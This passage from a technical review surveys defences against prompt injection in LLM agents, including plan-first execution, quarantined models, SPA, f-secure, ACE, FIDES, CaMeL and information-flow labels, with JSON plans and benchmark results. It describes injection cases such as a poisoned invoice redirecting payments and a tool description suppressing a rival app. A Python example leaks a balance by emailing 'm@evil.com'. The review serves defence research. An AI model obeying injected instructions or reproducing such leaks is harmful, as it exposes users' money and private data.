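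Willison's *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (2025) explains that the agent connected through an account that bypasses all row-level security. Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) objects that MCP does not bypass row-level security and that no customer had reported such a leak. These claims are compatible because the database applied its rules correctly, but the agent was using an account exempt from them.

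An account that could read only a view of the tickets would have prevented the leak, because the agent could not have read the private data. PromptQL also recommends running an agent's queries with the permissions of the person using it. That would probably not have helped here, since a developer can often read the whole database. The agent's access has to be limited to what the task requires, even when its user is entitled to more.

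Read-only access would have blocked this route, because the agent had to write the stolen data into the ticket. But the data would still have reached the model, and any other tool that sends text could have leaked it. Supabase offers a read-only mode and still considers prompt injection the main concern when that mode is on. It also tried wrapping query results in warnings and using classifiers. Both reduced the risk without eliminating it, and Supabase now advises developers never to connect agents directly to production data.

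### Compiling a question or refusing it

A list of approved queries is hard to use when people don't know what is on it. Wu describes a conversational system that addressed this problem for sales staff, based on work Wu led at Apple between 2021 and 2024. Its users could not read SQL, so they could not tell a wrong figure from a right one. Wu's rule is that any component that can make things up may influence which question the system answers, but never the value it returns.

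The system first extracts details such as the product, city, measure and date, and asks the user for any that are missing. It can use a language model to phrase these requests. Deterministic software then looks for a match among a few thousand question templates, which people who know the database wrote in advance. Each template specifies the table, the columns and the arithmetic. If one matches, the system restates the question in plain language and asks the user to confirm it. A compiler then turns the confirmed question into a query, always producing the same query for the same question, and the database computes the answer.

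If no template matches, the system writes no query and suggests the nearest questions it can answer. Wu calls this structural abstention. The system doesn't need to estimate whether to trust an answer, as other systems do after generating one, because it has no way to express an unsupported request.

For example, a user asks for sales at premium-tier and standard authorised stores in one city. Some stores belong to both classes, so adding the two totals would count them twice. The system detects the conflict and prompts the user to choose one class. A model writing its own SQL would probably return a believable number, and the user would not know how it had handled the overlap.

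The design does not guarantee a correct answer. Users may confirm a question without reading it properly, and a badly written template will give wrong figures without any warning. The software selects a template partly by sentence similarity, so it can pick one that is close but wrong, which the user then has to notice when confirming the question. Wu publishes no accuracy or usage figures, and acknowledges that nobody has tested the central claim that a visible refusal is better than a fluent but wrong answer.

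By the end of the project, the team was moving to an agent that assembled its own queries. Wu counts this as support for the rule, because the database still did the arithmetic. But the team gave up the closed set of queries that had constrained the system, so the case for keeping that set rests more on Wu's argument than on what happened at Apple.

Wu is also concerned with wrong figures, not attackers. A closed set of templates stops injected text from producing a new kind of query. But if the model fills in the customer's number, a template for looking up orders will still return any customer's orders, so the support agent would also need the session identifier.

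Wu suggests extending the rule to actions, so that a model could propose an action but only deterministic software could turn the confirmed proposal into a single, fixed effect. Wu presents this as a hypothesis and has not built it. The design would depend heavily on the confirmation step, and Anthropic's testers missed most of the dangerous commands they were asked to approve. People might judge a plain restatement of their own request more accurately than a shell command, but Wu offers no evidence on this.

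### A permitted read followed by a permitted send

Even well-designed limits on single calls miss harm that arises from a combination of calls. In an example from Adam and colleagues, a user asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a configuration file from an old one, and then to publish the project on GitHub. The file contains a private key, which the agent publishes with the project. Adam and colleagues observed this with Claude 4.5 Haiku, and it involved no attacker.

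The user asked for both steps, and neither call is suspicious by itself. Limiting the publishing tool to the user's own GitHub account would not help, because the published project would still contain the key. Cutting off the agent's network access would prevent the leak, but it would also block all publishing, and Adam and colleagues expect users to disable such a restriction quickly.

The support agent has the same problem if it can also search the web. It is allowed to read customer 4172's delivery address and to send search queries, so it can send her address to an outside company in a query. A filter might recognise a street address, but it could not tell a private address from one the customer wants to look up. To do that, it would need to know where the text came from, which the search call does not record.

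## Writing the whole plan before any tool runs

In plan-first execution, the agent writes a plan that lists every call before it makes any of them. This plan records where the text of a search comes from. The planner, the model that turns the user's request into a plan, receives the request and the list of tools, but none of the emails, files or web pages that the tools later return. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) describes the principle as planning in a trusted state, then executing the fixed plan in a state that may not be trustworthy.

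### Design patterns for agents that read untrusted text

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, describe six patterns for building agents that resist prompt injection. They doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable guarantees, so each pattern limits what the agent can do. Once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger a harmful action.

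The strictest pattern is the action selector. A customer-service bot using it picks from a fixed list of actions, such as sending a link to the customer's last order, and never reads what those actions return. In the more permissive plan-then-execute pattern, an assistant asked to send today's schedule to the user's boss, John Doe, plans two calls before making either: one to read the calendar and one to email John Doe. Malicious instructions in a calendar entry cannot change the recipient or add a third call, but they can change the body of the email.

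Turning calendar entries into a readable schedule usually takes a model, and that model has to read any hostile entry among them. One solution uses two models. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, a commentary on the paper of the same name, Willison (2025) traces this solution to his own proposal of April 2023. The planner can call tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that cannot call tools or change the plan. Ordinary software stores the quarantined model's answer under a name such as `$VAR`, and the planner can pass that name to a tool without seeing the answer.

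The map-reduce pattern gives each document to a separate quarantined model. If each model may only answer whether its file is an invoice, a hostile file can at most be miscounted as an invoice. In code-then-execute, which CaMeL uses, the planner writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models. Context minimisation mainly guards against a malicious user, by deleting the user's prompt before the model writes its reply.

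Several of these patterns rely on a narrow format to keep instructions out of the quarantined model's answer. This works for a yes or no, but even a short text can contain an instruction. For programming agents, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest having a quarantined model reduce outside documentation to a formal description in which, for example, method names have at most 30 characters. Willison wonders whether an attacker could still cause havoc within that limit, with a method named `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance()`.

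### The six steps of SPA's plan language

In *SPA*, Girrens and Wang combine a fixed plan with a quarantined model and give the planner its own small language. A plan is a JSON list built from six kinds of step.

| Step | What it does | What a checker can find by looking for it |
|---|---|---|
| `retrieve` | loads a stored result from an earlier request | where old data enters the plan |
| `tool` | calls a tool with given arguments | where the plan can affect the outside world |
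| `q-llm` | gives data to the quarantined model and specifies the format of its answer | where a model interprets untrusted text |
| `display` | shows text and values to the user | where data reaches the user |
| `condition` | runs one of two lists of steps, depending on a test | which steps depend on a decision, and on which data |
| `loop` | runs a list of steps once for each item in a collection | which steps repeat, and over what |

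The test in a `condition` step uses one of eight operators. Six compare two values (equal, unequal, less, less or equal, greater, greater or equal), `in` tests whether a collection contains an item, and `exists` tests whether a value is present. There is no "and" or "or", so a planner combines tests by nesting `condition` steps. Each decision depends only on the values in one test, and the checker can identify which data determined whether a step ran.

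Arguments are similarly limited to fixed values, variables, fields of variables, and lists or objects made from these. They cannot contain arithmetic, text templates or user-defined functions. If a plan could pass `clean(account)` to a payment tool, the checker could not generally determine what `clean` does without running it. Without functions, an argument names the variables it uses.

The restriction makes some ordinary tasks awkward. A plan cannot add a 10% tip to a bill, so the planner has to find a tool that does the arithmetic or pass the calculation to the quarantined model. SPA's instructions allow the planner to use the quarantined model for simple totals, but that model can make arithmetic mistakes, and its input may contain hostile text.

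Loops can only iterate over collections, and the language has no recursion, so every plan finishes if its tool and model calls finish.

Before a plan runs, a validator checks that each step has the required fields and that every variable has a value before a step uses it. No step may overwrite a variable, and variables created inside a branch or loop cannot be used outside it. The interpreter, the program that carries out the plan, compares each call's arguments with the tool's schema only when it makes that call.

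### An invoice fetched on Monday and paid on Tuesday

Girrens and Wang illustrate the danger of stored data with an invoice. On Monday, a user asks the agent to fetch an invoice from a company named Acme and keep the details for later. In SPA's format, with invented tool and file names, the plan might be:

```json
{"steps": [
  {"type": "tool",
   "tool_name": "read_file",
   "inputs": {"path": "acme-invoice.txt"},
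   "output": "file",
   "intent": "Fetch the Acme invoice",
   "output_semantics": "Text of the Acme invoice"},
  {"type": "q-llm",
   "inputs": [{"var": "file"}],
   "prompt": "Extract the account to pay and the amount due.",
   "output_schema": {
     "type": "object",
     "properties": {"account": {"type": "string"},
                    "amount": {"type": "number"}},
     "required": ["account", "amount"],
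     "additionalProperties": false},
   "output": "details",
   "intent": "Extract the payment details",
   "output_semantics": "Account and amount on the Acme invoice"},
  {"type": "display",
   "items": ["Invoice saved. Amount due:",
             {"attr": {"var": "details", "path": ["amount"]}}]}
]}
```

The planner writes all of this in a single call. Its prompt contains the rules of the language, three worked examples, the list of tools, descriptions of any stored results and the user's request. The validator then checks the plan. SPA's full version adds a further check that tracks secrecy and trust through the plan.

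If the plan passes, the interpreter runs the steps in order. It calls `read_file`, either in the agent's process or in a container with no network access, and checks the result against the tool's schema. It then sends only the invoice text and the step's prompt to the quarantined model, which must return an account and an amount in the specified format. Finally, the interpreter shows the amount to the user.

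On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice from the day before. The planner writes a new plan:

```json
{"steps": [
  {"type": "retrieve",
   "artifact_id": "acme_details",
   "output": "invoice"},
  {"type": "tool",
   "tool_name": "send_money",
   "inputs": {
     "recipient": {"attr": {"var": "invoice", "path": ["account"]}},
     "amount": {"attr": {"var": "invoice", "path": ["amount"]}}},
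   "output": "receipt",
   "intent": "Pay the Acme invoice",
   "output_semantics": "Confirmation of the payment"},
  {"type": "display",
   "items": ["Payment result:", {"var": "receipt"}]}
]}
```

Suppose the planner had misspelled `invoice` in the payment step. The validator would find a variable that no earlier step had defined, and SPA would end the request with a failure, without sending the error back to the planner or asking for a corrected plan. SPA also ends the request if a tool fails or a field is missing while the plan is running. By then, earlier steps may already have sent an email or paid a bill.

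The lack of plan repair is deliberate. An error message from a tool could carry an attacker's text to the planner. If the planner received the checker's reasons for rejecting a plan, it could also keep revising the plan until an unsafe version passed.

### Reusing results that the planner cannot read

On Tuesday, the planner had to choose `acme_details` without seeing its contents. After a successful run, SPA stores each result from a tool or the quarantined model in separate parts, including the value and a description. A later planner sees only the description, which consists of the result's format, the request that produced it, and the `intent` and `output_semantics` fields. Monday's planner wrote those two fields before any tool had opened the invoice, so the invoice's text could not influence them. The account number stays hidden until the interpreter reaches the `retrieve` step.

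To test this, Girrens and Wang split AgentDojo's 97 user tasks into conversations of two to five requests, in which later requests need earlier results. When the needed result was in storage, the later plan retrieved it 95.4% of the time. Including cases where an earlier plan had failed to store anything lowers the rate to 80.1%. Both rates are for SPA without its label checks.

Showing the planner the stored values instead of hiding them raised the overall task completion rate only slightly, from 62.5% to 65.9%. Completion rose by 25 percentage points in banking but fell by 20 in travel, which has only 20 tasks. The attack success rate rose from 0.3% to 0.6%. That small rise is weak evidence that showing stored values is safe, because AgentDojo's attacks were not written to remain inactive in storage until a later request.

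### What a fixed plan guarantees

A tool's output cannot add, remove or reorder steps. If the Acme invoice contains an instruction to email the user's files to a stranger, the instruction has no effect, because neither plan has a step that sends email. Data can still determine which branch of a `condition` runs and how often a loop repeats, but the planner wrote all the available steps in advance. The guarantee holds only if the validator and interpreter work correctly and the user's request is trustworthy. If the user pastes an attacker's text into the request, the planner will read it, and it could influence the plan.

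The guarantee does not cover the values that the steps use. An attacker can print a different account number on the invoice, without any instruction, or add a line telling the quarantined model which account to return. Either way, the answer is a string that fits the schema, and Tuesday's plan sends the money to the attacker. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), a formal treatment of such defences, likewise concludes that in agents with a quarantined model, an injection cannot add a call but can make an answer wrong, which the plan then uses. In one of its examples, a fixed plan leaks data because the quarantined model copies private notes into a reply that the plan sends.

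A payment tool that accepted only saved payees would help, but it could not pay a new supplier. SPA instead uses label checks, which block payments like this one but also many legitimate ones.

### f-secure plans one step at a time

SPA hides all results from the planner, including trustworthy ones. *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) presents a less strict system, f-secure. Its planner writes one step, waits for it to run and then writes the next. A security monitor passes the planner only results from trusted sources.

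In one test, the user asks the agent to read emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns two emails from colleagues, with budgets of $724 and $1,024, and one from an outsider telling the agent to send all the budgets to Mallory. The monitor passes only the colleagues' emails to the planner, so the planner correctly decides to notify the manager.

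Each step has five fields: a number, an instruction, the tool or model that carries it out, its inputs and its output. A reference such as `{Data_output:1}` stands for a result that the planner may not see. Wu and colleagues prove that untrusted data cannot influence the steps. Let $q$ be the user's request, $\pi_q$ a sequence of steps, and $Q_1$ and $Q_2$ two versions of all the data the system might read. If the two versions contain the same trusted data, then

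$$\Pr[\pi_q \mid q, Q_1] = \Pr[\pi_q \mid q, Q_2].$$

An attacker who rewrites every untrusted email therefore cannot make any sequence of steps more or less likely. In practice, retries could weaken this guarantee. When a step fails, the planner in f-secure generates another, so an attacker whose data can make certain steps fail might influence which step eventually succeeds. The proof does not cover attacks that stop a tool from working. SPA avoids the problem by not retrying.

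f-secure has the same gap as SPA's fixed plan, since it doesn't check whether each argument comes from a trusted source. It also assumes that tool descriptions are trustworthy, and its planner reads them.

### ACE hides the installed tools from the planner

*ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2025) shows how a tool's description can distort a plan. In one example, a user wants to know the fare for a trip and has two apps that can calculate it, MetroHail and QuickRide. QuickRide's description includes an instruction to leave MetroHail out of the plan. The planner in IsolateGPT, an earlier defence, followed the instruction, so the user saw only QuickRide's fare.

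ACE's planner has no information about the installed apps. A model uses only the user's request to define new abstract tools the task seems to need, each with a name, a description, and types for its inputs and output. For a request to summarize `file.txt`, these might be `DocumentLoader` and `TextSummarizer`. The planner then uses a restricted form of Python to write a program that calls these tools.

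Next, ACE looks for an installed app for each abstract tool. It narrows the candidates by comparing descriptions, then has a model judge each remaining pairing of tool and app separately and write code to convert between their formats. QuickRide's description can no longer exclude MetroHail, because the model does not read it when considering MetroHail. If several combinations of apps would work, ACE prefers one that needs fewer permissions. A dishonest app can still describe itself as a fare calculator and return a false fare.

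Both ACE and f-secure stopped every attack in InjecAgent, a benchmark of 1,054 cases in which a tool's output contains an instruction to misuse another tool. In the benchmark's basic version, 28.7% of attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent running GPT-4 Turbo, according to Wu and colleagues. These results mostly confirm that ACE and f-secure work as designed. ACE never puts an app's output into a model's prompt, and f-secure's planner never receives untrusted output, so the attacker's instruction could not have reached either planner.

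ACE completed 75.2% of the user tasks in this benchmark when GPT-4o did the planning and o3-mini matched the apps. It found the right app in 82.1% of cases, and 91.7% of those then ran without errors. When GPT-4o did both jobs, ACE completed only 47.2%, mainly because it found the right app less often.

### How many tasks SPA completes

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on a newer version of AgentDojo that has the same 97 user tasks but 949 security cases. They used gpt-5.4-nano, a small model, as both the planner and the quarantined model. The attacker knew which tools each task required. The table shows the results without label checks.

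| Planner sees | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| installed tools | 53.0% | 54.7% | 0.4% |
| abstract tools only | 14.1% | 11.7% | 0.0% |

The 0.4% corresponds to four successful attacks, all on one banking task. Three caused unauthorised transfers and one changed the user's password. In each, injected text passed through the quarantined model and reached a tool that should have received only trusted data, which is the gap described above. The interpreter cannot add steps, so the plan must already have included one that could change the password. An overly broad plan therefore gives an attacker more steps to exploit.

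The 53.0% completion rate is harder to interpret. About 81% of runs executed the plan. Most of the rest presumably failed validation, and a system that repaired plans might have saved some of them. Many of the plans that ran were incomplete or wrong. The experiment compares versions of SPA only with one another. Without results for an ordinary agent running the same model, we cannot tell how many tasks failed because the plan was fixed and how many failed because the planner was weak.

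Abstract tools clearly hurt performance a lot. About 75% of those runs failed because SPA could not match an invented tool to an installed one, and no travel task succeeded. Even the 14.1% figure is too high, because five banking tasks passed AgentDojo's checks without the agent completing anything. Those five account for about a third of the paper's weighted average. The zero attack success rate is weak evidence of security because so few plans ran.

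ACE scored much higher, at 75.2%, but on different tasks and with a looser measure, which counts a task as completed if the right app ran and returned valid output. The gap between ACE's own configurations suggests that a better matching model would also help SPA, but nobody has measured how much.

### Tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads

The main objection to plan-first execution is that an agent often cannot know what to do until it has read something. A fixed plan can handle some of these tasks. *SecPO* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to check the rating of the running shoes bought that day and, if it is below 4.0, to buy another pair for no more than $100. The rating is 3.2, so the agent buys a pair rated 4.4 for $80.49. SPA's language could express this with a `condition` on the rating, followed by a search, a `q-llm` step to choose the shoes, and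 a purchase. But the quarantined model would choose from sellers' listings, so a hostile listing might influence its choice.

Other tasks are much harder to plan in advance. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that has to plot last week's sales, but the billing service has replaced the address the agent used to fetch the data. The agent needs to read the new documentation and change its request. In another example, an agent has to fix failing software tests, and each repair changes what fails next. A planner could add branches for a few foreseeable errors, but not for every possible one. Branches also let an attacker who controls the value a branch tests choose which steps run.

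AgentDojo hardly measures this weakness, because only 6 of its 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) introduces a benchmark of 60 tasks that all do. The data in these tasks also includes helpful instructions, such as a checkout page's request to log in first. Defences that rely on an initial plan, including CaMeL, completed far fewer tasks on this benchmark. SPA has results only for AgentDojo and its multi-request version, so its 53.0% probably overstates how well it would do on tasks like these.

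Some defences give up the fixed plan. *SecPO* trains the model to resist injected instructions, and the trained model completed 43 of AgentDyn's 60 tasks, the same number as the untrained one. *ActGuard* (2026) describes an agent that predicts only which tools it might use next. A call to any other tool is treated as a possible sign of attack but may still go ahead after an audit. Xiang and colleagues propose letting the agent revise its plan and having a model judge each revision from a structured description of the change, without seeing the raw text behind it. They accept that relying on a model's judgement rules out a complete formal guarantee.

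With SPA, the user, rather than the planner, reads the result of one request and can adapt the plan by making another. SPA completed 60.8% of tasks when Girrens and Wang split them up in this way and 52.6% when they did not, counting every task equally, although the wording and scoring also differed. The user can also be deceived and may, for example, ask the agent to pay a false account number shown on the screen.

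## Tracking secrecy and trust through a plan

A fixed plan will pay whatever account number is on Acme's invoice. To refuse that payment, a checker needs a record that the number came from an outsider and a rule that the payment tool should not accept such numbers. Information-flow control provides both. It labels every value, updates the labels as a program copies and combines values, and checks them against a policy before the values reach a tool.

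The idea of tracking secrecy and trust dates from the 1970s. *SPA*'s rule for secrecy is that sensitive data should not flow to a destination that lacks the authority to receive it. The paper traces this rule to a 1973 report by Bell and LaPadula for MITRE, an American research organisation. In 1976, Denning described a general model in which every value has a security class and may flow only where the ordering of the classes allows. Biba's 1977 report, also for MITRE, covers trust, with the rule that data from a doubtful source should not influence anything that requires reliable data.

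### Two orderings and a flow rule

A label in SPA has a confidentiality level, which records how secret a value is, and an integrity level, which records how trustworthy its source is. In the simplest version, public is below private and untrusted is below trusted. An operator can define more levels, and some may be unranked relative to each other, as the levels for medical and payroll records might be.

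When a step combines two values, the result is as secret as the more secret one and only as trustworthy as the less trustworthy one. If the values have confidentiality levels $c_1$ and $c_2$ and integrity levels $i_1$ and $i_2$, the result has levels $c$ and $i$, where

$$c = c_1 \sqcup_C c_2 \quad \text{and} \quad i = i_1 \sqcap_I i_2.$$

Here $\sqcup_C$ gives the lowest confidentiality level at or above both inputs, and $\sqcap_I$ gives the highest integrity level at or below both.

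A value $s$ may flow to a destination $d$ only if

$$C(s) \sqsubseteq_C C(d) \quad \text{and} \quad I(d) \sqsubseteq_I I(s),$$

where $\sqsubseteq$ means "at or below". The destination must be cleared for data at least as secret as the value, and the value must be at least as trustworthy as the destination requires. The first condition is Bell and LaPadula's and the second is Biba's.

A system can also represent confidentiality as a list of permitted readers. If Alice, Ben and Carol may read one document, and Ben, Carol and Dan may read another, only Ben and Carol may read a text based on both. A mail tool can then check that every recipient is on the list.

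In SPA, the operator gives each tool two labels. One sets the highest secrecy and the lowest trust that the tool accepts in its inputs. The other sets a baseline for its output, because a tool's arguments may reveal little about what it returns. For example, a mailbox search for the word "lunch" can return private messages written by strangers.

### The invoice plan with labels

Suppose the operator treats the user's requests as private and trusted, and file contents as private and untrusted. The checker would label Monday's and Tuesday's plans as follows.

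| Step | What it uses | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| Monday: `read_file` | a file name from the request (private, trusted) | invoice text: private, untrusted |
| Monday: `q-llm` | the invoice text | account and amount: private, untrusted |
| Monday: `display` | the amount | shown, if the operator lets the user see private, untrusted values |
| Tuesday: `retrieve` | the stored details | account and amount, still private and untrusted |
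| Tuesday: `send_money` | the account and the amount | refused, because the tool requires trusted input |

Monday's plan passes the check. SPA stores the labels with the results, so the account number is still untrusted on Tuesday, and Tuesday's plan fails before any of its steps run. It would fail even if the invoice were genuine, because the labels record where the number came from, not whether it is correct.

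The quarantined model doesn't change this outcome. Its answer has the combined label of everything it read, because the software cannot work out which parts of an answer depend on which parts of the input. A summary of an untrusted email is therefore untrusted. If the answer counted as trusted, an attacker could make any value count as trusted by having a model repeat it.

Payment works if the account comes from a trusted source. Suppose the user says, "Pay Acme the $480 I owe, using the account in my address book." The first two steps of the plan might be:

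```json
[
  {"type": "tool",
   "tool_name": "find_payee",
   "inputs": {"name": "Acme"},
   "output": "payee",
   "intent": "Look up Acme in the address book",
   "output_semantics": "Acme's saved payment details"},
  {"type": "tool",
   "tool_name": "send_money",
   "inputs": {
     "recipient": {"attr": {"var": "payee", "path": ["account"]}},
     "amount": 480},
   "output": "receipt",
   "intent": "Pay Acme",
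   "output_semantics": "Confirmation of the payment"}
]
```

The name and the amount have the label of the user's request, and the operator has marked the address book as private and trusted. Every input to `send_money` is therefore trusted, and the plan passes. If the plan took the amount from the invoice, SPA would refuse it even though the other inputs are trusted, because SPA combines the labels of all the arguments before comparing them with the tool's requirement. The check relies on the operator having labeled the address book correctly. If the mail program automatically saves details from incoming messages, an attacker could add a false entry that SPA would treat as trusted.

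### Flows through decisions

Untrusted data can influence a payment without supplying any of its arguments. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay Acme $480 if the invoice is marked overdue. The account comes from the address book and the amount from the request, but whoever writes the invoice controls whether the agent pays. This is an implicit flow, in which data affects an action through a decision.

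To catch it, SPA keeps a label for the current position in the plan, called the program-counter label. It starts as the label of the user's request. Inside a `condition`, SPA combines it with the labels of the values in the test, and inside a `loop`, with the label of the collection. Every step inside is at least as secret as the combined label and at most as trusted. SPA therefore treats the payment in the overdue branch as untrusted and refuses the plan.

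Secrets can leak in the same way. If a plan posts "Away today" on a public page only when the user's calendar contains a hospital appointment, the post reveals the appointment even though its wording is harmless. The absence of a post reveals that there is no appointment, so SPA checks both branches under the same label.

It is easy to get this wrong when labelling a program as it runs. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, report a leak in CaMeL, whose planner writes a program. CaMeL correctly blocks an email sent directly from a branch that tests a private bank balance. The leak takes a detour through two variables, roughly like this:

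```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the first branch sets `tmp` to false and marks it private. The program then skips the second branch, so `rich` stays true and public, and CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether an email arrives. CaMeL raises a variable's label only in a branch that runs, so `rich` stays public when the second branch is skipped, even though its value reveals the balance. Fenton described the underlying trick in 1974.

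SPA's limits on overwriting and reusing variables rule out this version, and its checker examines both branches before anything runs.

### FIDES also labels the planner's context

SPA's planner never receives a tool's output, so SPA needs labels only on the values in the plan. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system whose planner chooses one call at a time and may read the results before choosing the next. Anything it reads could influence its later choices, so FIDES also labels the planner's context, which is the whole conversation so far, by combining the labels of everything in it.

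When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares its label with the context's. If the result is no more secret and no less trustworthy than the context, the planner sees it. Otherwise, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. FIDES does this field by field, so the planner may see part of a result while the rest stays hidden.

The planner can still pass a hidden value to a tool or to a quarantined model. If it sends a colleague a summary of emails hidden from it, the summary is untrusted, but the decision to send it and the choice of recipient are trusted. FIDES labels the decision and each argument separately, so a policy can require the choice of recipient to be trusted without requiring the same of the message.

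The planner can also inspect a variable, which SPA does not allow. This helps with tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads, such as completing the items on a to-do list. But if the list is untrusted, the whole context becomes untrusted once the planner has read it. FIDES then blocks any later call that requires a trusted decision, though the planner can still make harmless calls, such as further searches.

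Costa and colleagues report that FIDES, with suitable policies, stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo, though Garby and colleagues note that it discounts two of the benchmark's injections as outside the scope of its policies. With the policies enforced, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic labelled planner when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more when both used OpenAI's o1. With the policy checks off, hiding values from the planner reduced the number of completed tasks by 6.3% compared with the basic planner. Practical attacks could also succeed again, so the protection depends on the policies as well as on hiding text from the planner.

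Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES satisfies a limited property called explicit secrecy. This property rules out copying private data to a place the attacker can read, but it doesn't prevent the attacker from inferring private information from the sequence of tool calls. If an agent reads a private balance and then decides whether to update a public page, the update itself may reveal something about the balance. Costa and colleagues chose this limit deliberately. Closing the gap would essentially require forbidding any call with publicly visible effects once the agent has called a tool that may read private data.

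### Noninterference and the LLMbda calculus

Noninterference is the stronger property. A program is noninterfering if two runs whose inputs differ only in data that a particular observer is not allowed to see always look the same to that observer. For secrecy, this means that changing private data never changes public output, and for trust, that changing untrusted data never changes trusted output. Wu and colleagues proved a property of this kind for the steps that f-secure's planner writes.

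Garby and colleagues prove a version for a whole programming language, the LLMbda calculus. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which everything is built from functions. The added operations prompt a model, copy a conversation for temporary use and clear a conversation. A program can also run code that the model writes. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation. A developer can therefore write a quarantined model as an ordinary program that copies the conversation, clears the copy and prompts the model there. SPA and FIDES instead build this separation into the system.

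A language model's output is random, so the theorem compares probabilities. Take two starting points that look the same to an observer, and let $\mu_0(q)$ and $\mu_1(q)$ be the probabilities that each leads to a visible outcome $q$. Ideally these would be equal. But some runs never finish, and a label check stops others, so each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1. The theorem guarantees that a single set of probabilities $\omega$, adding up to at most 1, satisfies

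$$\mu_0(q) \leq \omega(q) \quad \text{and} \quad \mu_1(q) \leq \omega(q) \quad \text{for every } q.$$

If both programs always finish, $\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ must be identical. Otherwise, hidden data can influence whether a run finishes, and the effect on the visible outcomes is limited. If $d_0$ and $d_1$ are the probabilities of not finishing, then

$$\frac{1}{2}\sum_q \left|\mu_0(q) - \mu_1(q)\right| \leq \frac{d_0 + d_1}{2}.$$

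If each fails to finish 2% of the time, for example, the two distributions differ by at most 0.02.

To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs that skips a computation as soon as its label becomes too high for the observer and puts a dummy value in its place. The result cannot depend on the hidden data, so it is the same for both starting points. A program run this way also finishes at least as often as the original, which gives the required $\omega$.

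The small leak that the theorem permits matters if an attacker can repeat it. CaMeL retries failed programs in an ordinary Python loop outside its label tracking. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and Garby and colleagues explain that repeated attempts could extract all of it. Their agent, Randori, runs its retry loop inside the labelled language. It tests and repairs its program on artificial data, where it can safely read every error message, and only then uses the real data. SPA avoids the danger by never repairing a plan.

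The theorem covers every program in the LLMbda calculus, including any code the model writes, but not agents written in Python or other languages. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, software that verifies each step of a mathematical argument. The interpreter that runs the agents is also written in Lean, and another checked theorem shows that it matches the language's definition. To their knowledge, no earlier agent software had machine-checked security theorems about the program that actually runs.

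The proof does not cover the network request to the model, which is unverified code, and the theorem about the interpreter assumes that the model's responses follow a fixed probability distribution for each conversation. The developer must also label data sources correctly and put checks on sensitive tools. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that the language assumes all data sources are part of the program. The bank in their tests was a simulation written in the language itself, so an agent connected to a real bank would also depend on unverified code.

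### What SPA's label checks cost and prevented

Girrens and Wang ran the same AgentDojo tests with and without SPA's label checks. The planner saw the installed tools in both versions.

| | Without label checks | With label checks |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed, no attack | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 54.7% | 29.5% |
| Attack success rate, 949 attacked runs | 0.4% | 0.0% |
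| Runs that executed the plan | about 81% | about 37% |
| Runs that the label checks refused | none | about 53% |

The checks lowered the completion rate by 24 percentage points and prevented four attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. Most refusals happened because a plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted input. The share of runs that executed a plan fell by about 44 points, much more than the completion rate, so many of the refused plans would probably have failed anyway.

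The costs and the benefits fell in different places.

| Suite | Fall in completion, percentage points | Successful attacks without label checks |
|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 25.0 | 0 |
| Slack | 28.6 | 0 |
| Travel | 35.0 | 0 |
| Banking | 6.25 | 4 |

One sentence in *SPA* describes reductions of this size as falls in attack success. That cannot be right, because the attack success rate never exceeded 0.4%. The paper's appendix correctly describes the reductions as falls in completion.

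In workspace, Slack and travel, the checks blocked legitimate work but no attacks, because the fixed plan had already stopped every attack there. All four successful attacks were on a banking task that Garby and colleagues summarise as reading a file and following its instructions precisely. In banking, the checks blocked legitimate work equivalent to only one of the 16 tasks.

AgentDojo is a weak test of what label checks add, because a fixed plan already ignores most of its planted instructions. These figures alone may therefore understate the checks' value. Garby and colleagues found that 97 of the 144 banking cases required a tool call or file read that would never appear in a plan for the user's task. Label checks mainly add protection against an attacker who changes a value the plan uses, such as the account number on an invoice or the address on Dora's website.

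A fairer test would silently change such values in the benchmark's data and count how often each version of SPA acted on them. Girrens and Wang propose attacks in which an attacker's values become sensitive arguments, but leave them for future work. SPA would probably fail often without label checks. If the labels and policies were correct, the checks would stop every payment based on a changed value, but they would also stop payments based on unaltered invoices, so SPA would still complete fewer tasks with the checks on.

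When a later request used an earlier result, as in the invoice example, the checks reduced completion from 62.5% to 35.3% and attack success from 0.3% to 0.2%. The 0.2% consists of two travel runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks even though SPA had refused the plan.

Other systems lose tasks in the same way. When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking suite, turning on its policy checks reduced task completion from 66.7% to 37.5% with GPT-5.2 and from 70.8% to 37.5% with Xiaomi's MiMo-v2.5. These percentages are imprecise because they come from only 16 tasks, each run three times, but the fall is large for both models.

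### Finer labels and explicit endorsement

SPA labels each variable as a whole and sets one trust requirement for all of a tool's arguments. Girrens and Wang suggest labelling individual fields, setting separate requirements for individual arguments, and adding endorsement, which raises a value's trust after an explicit check. FIDES already has the first two.

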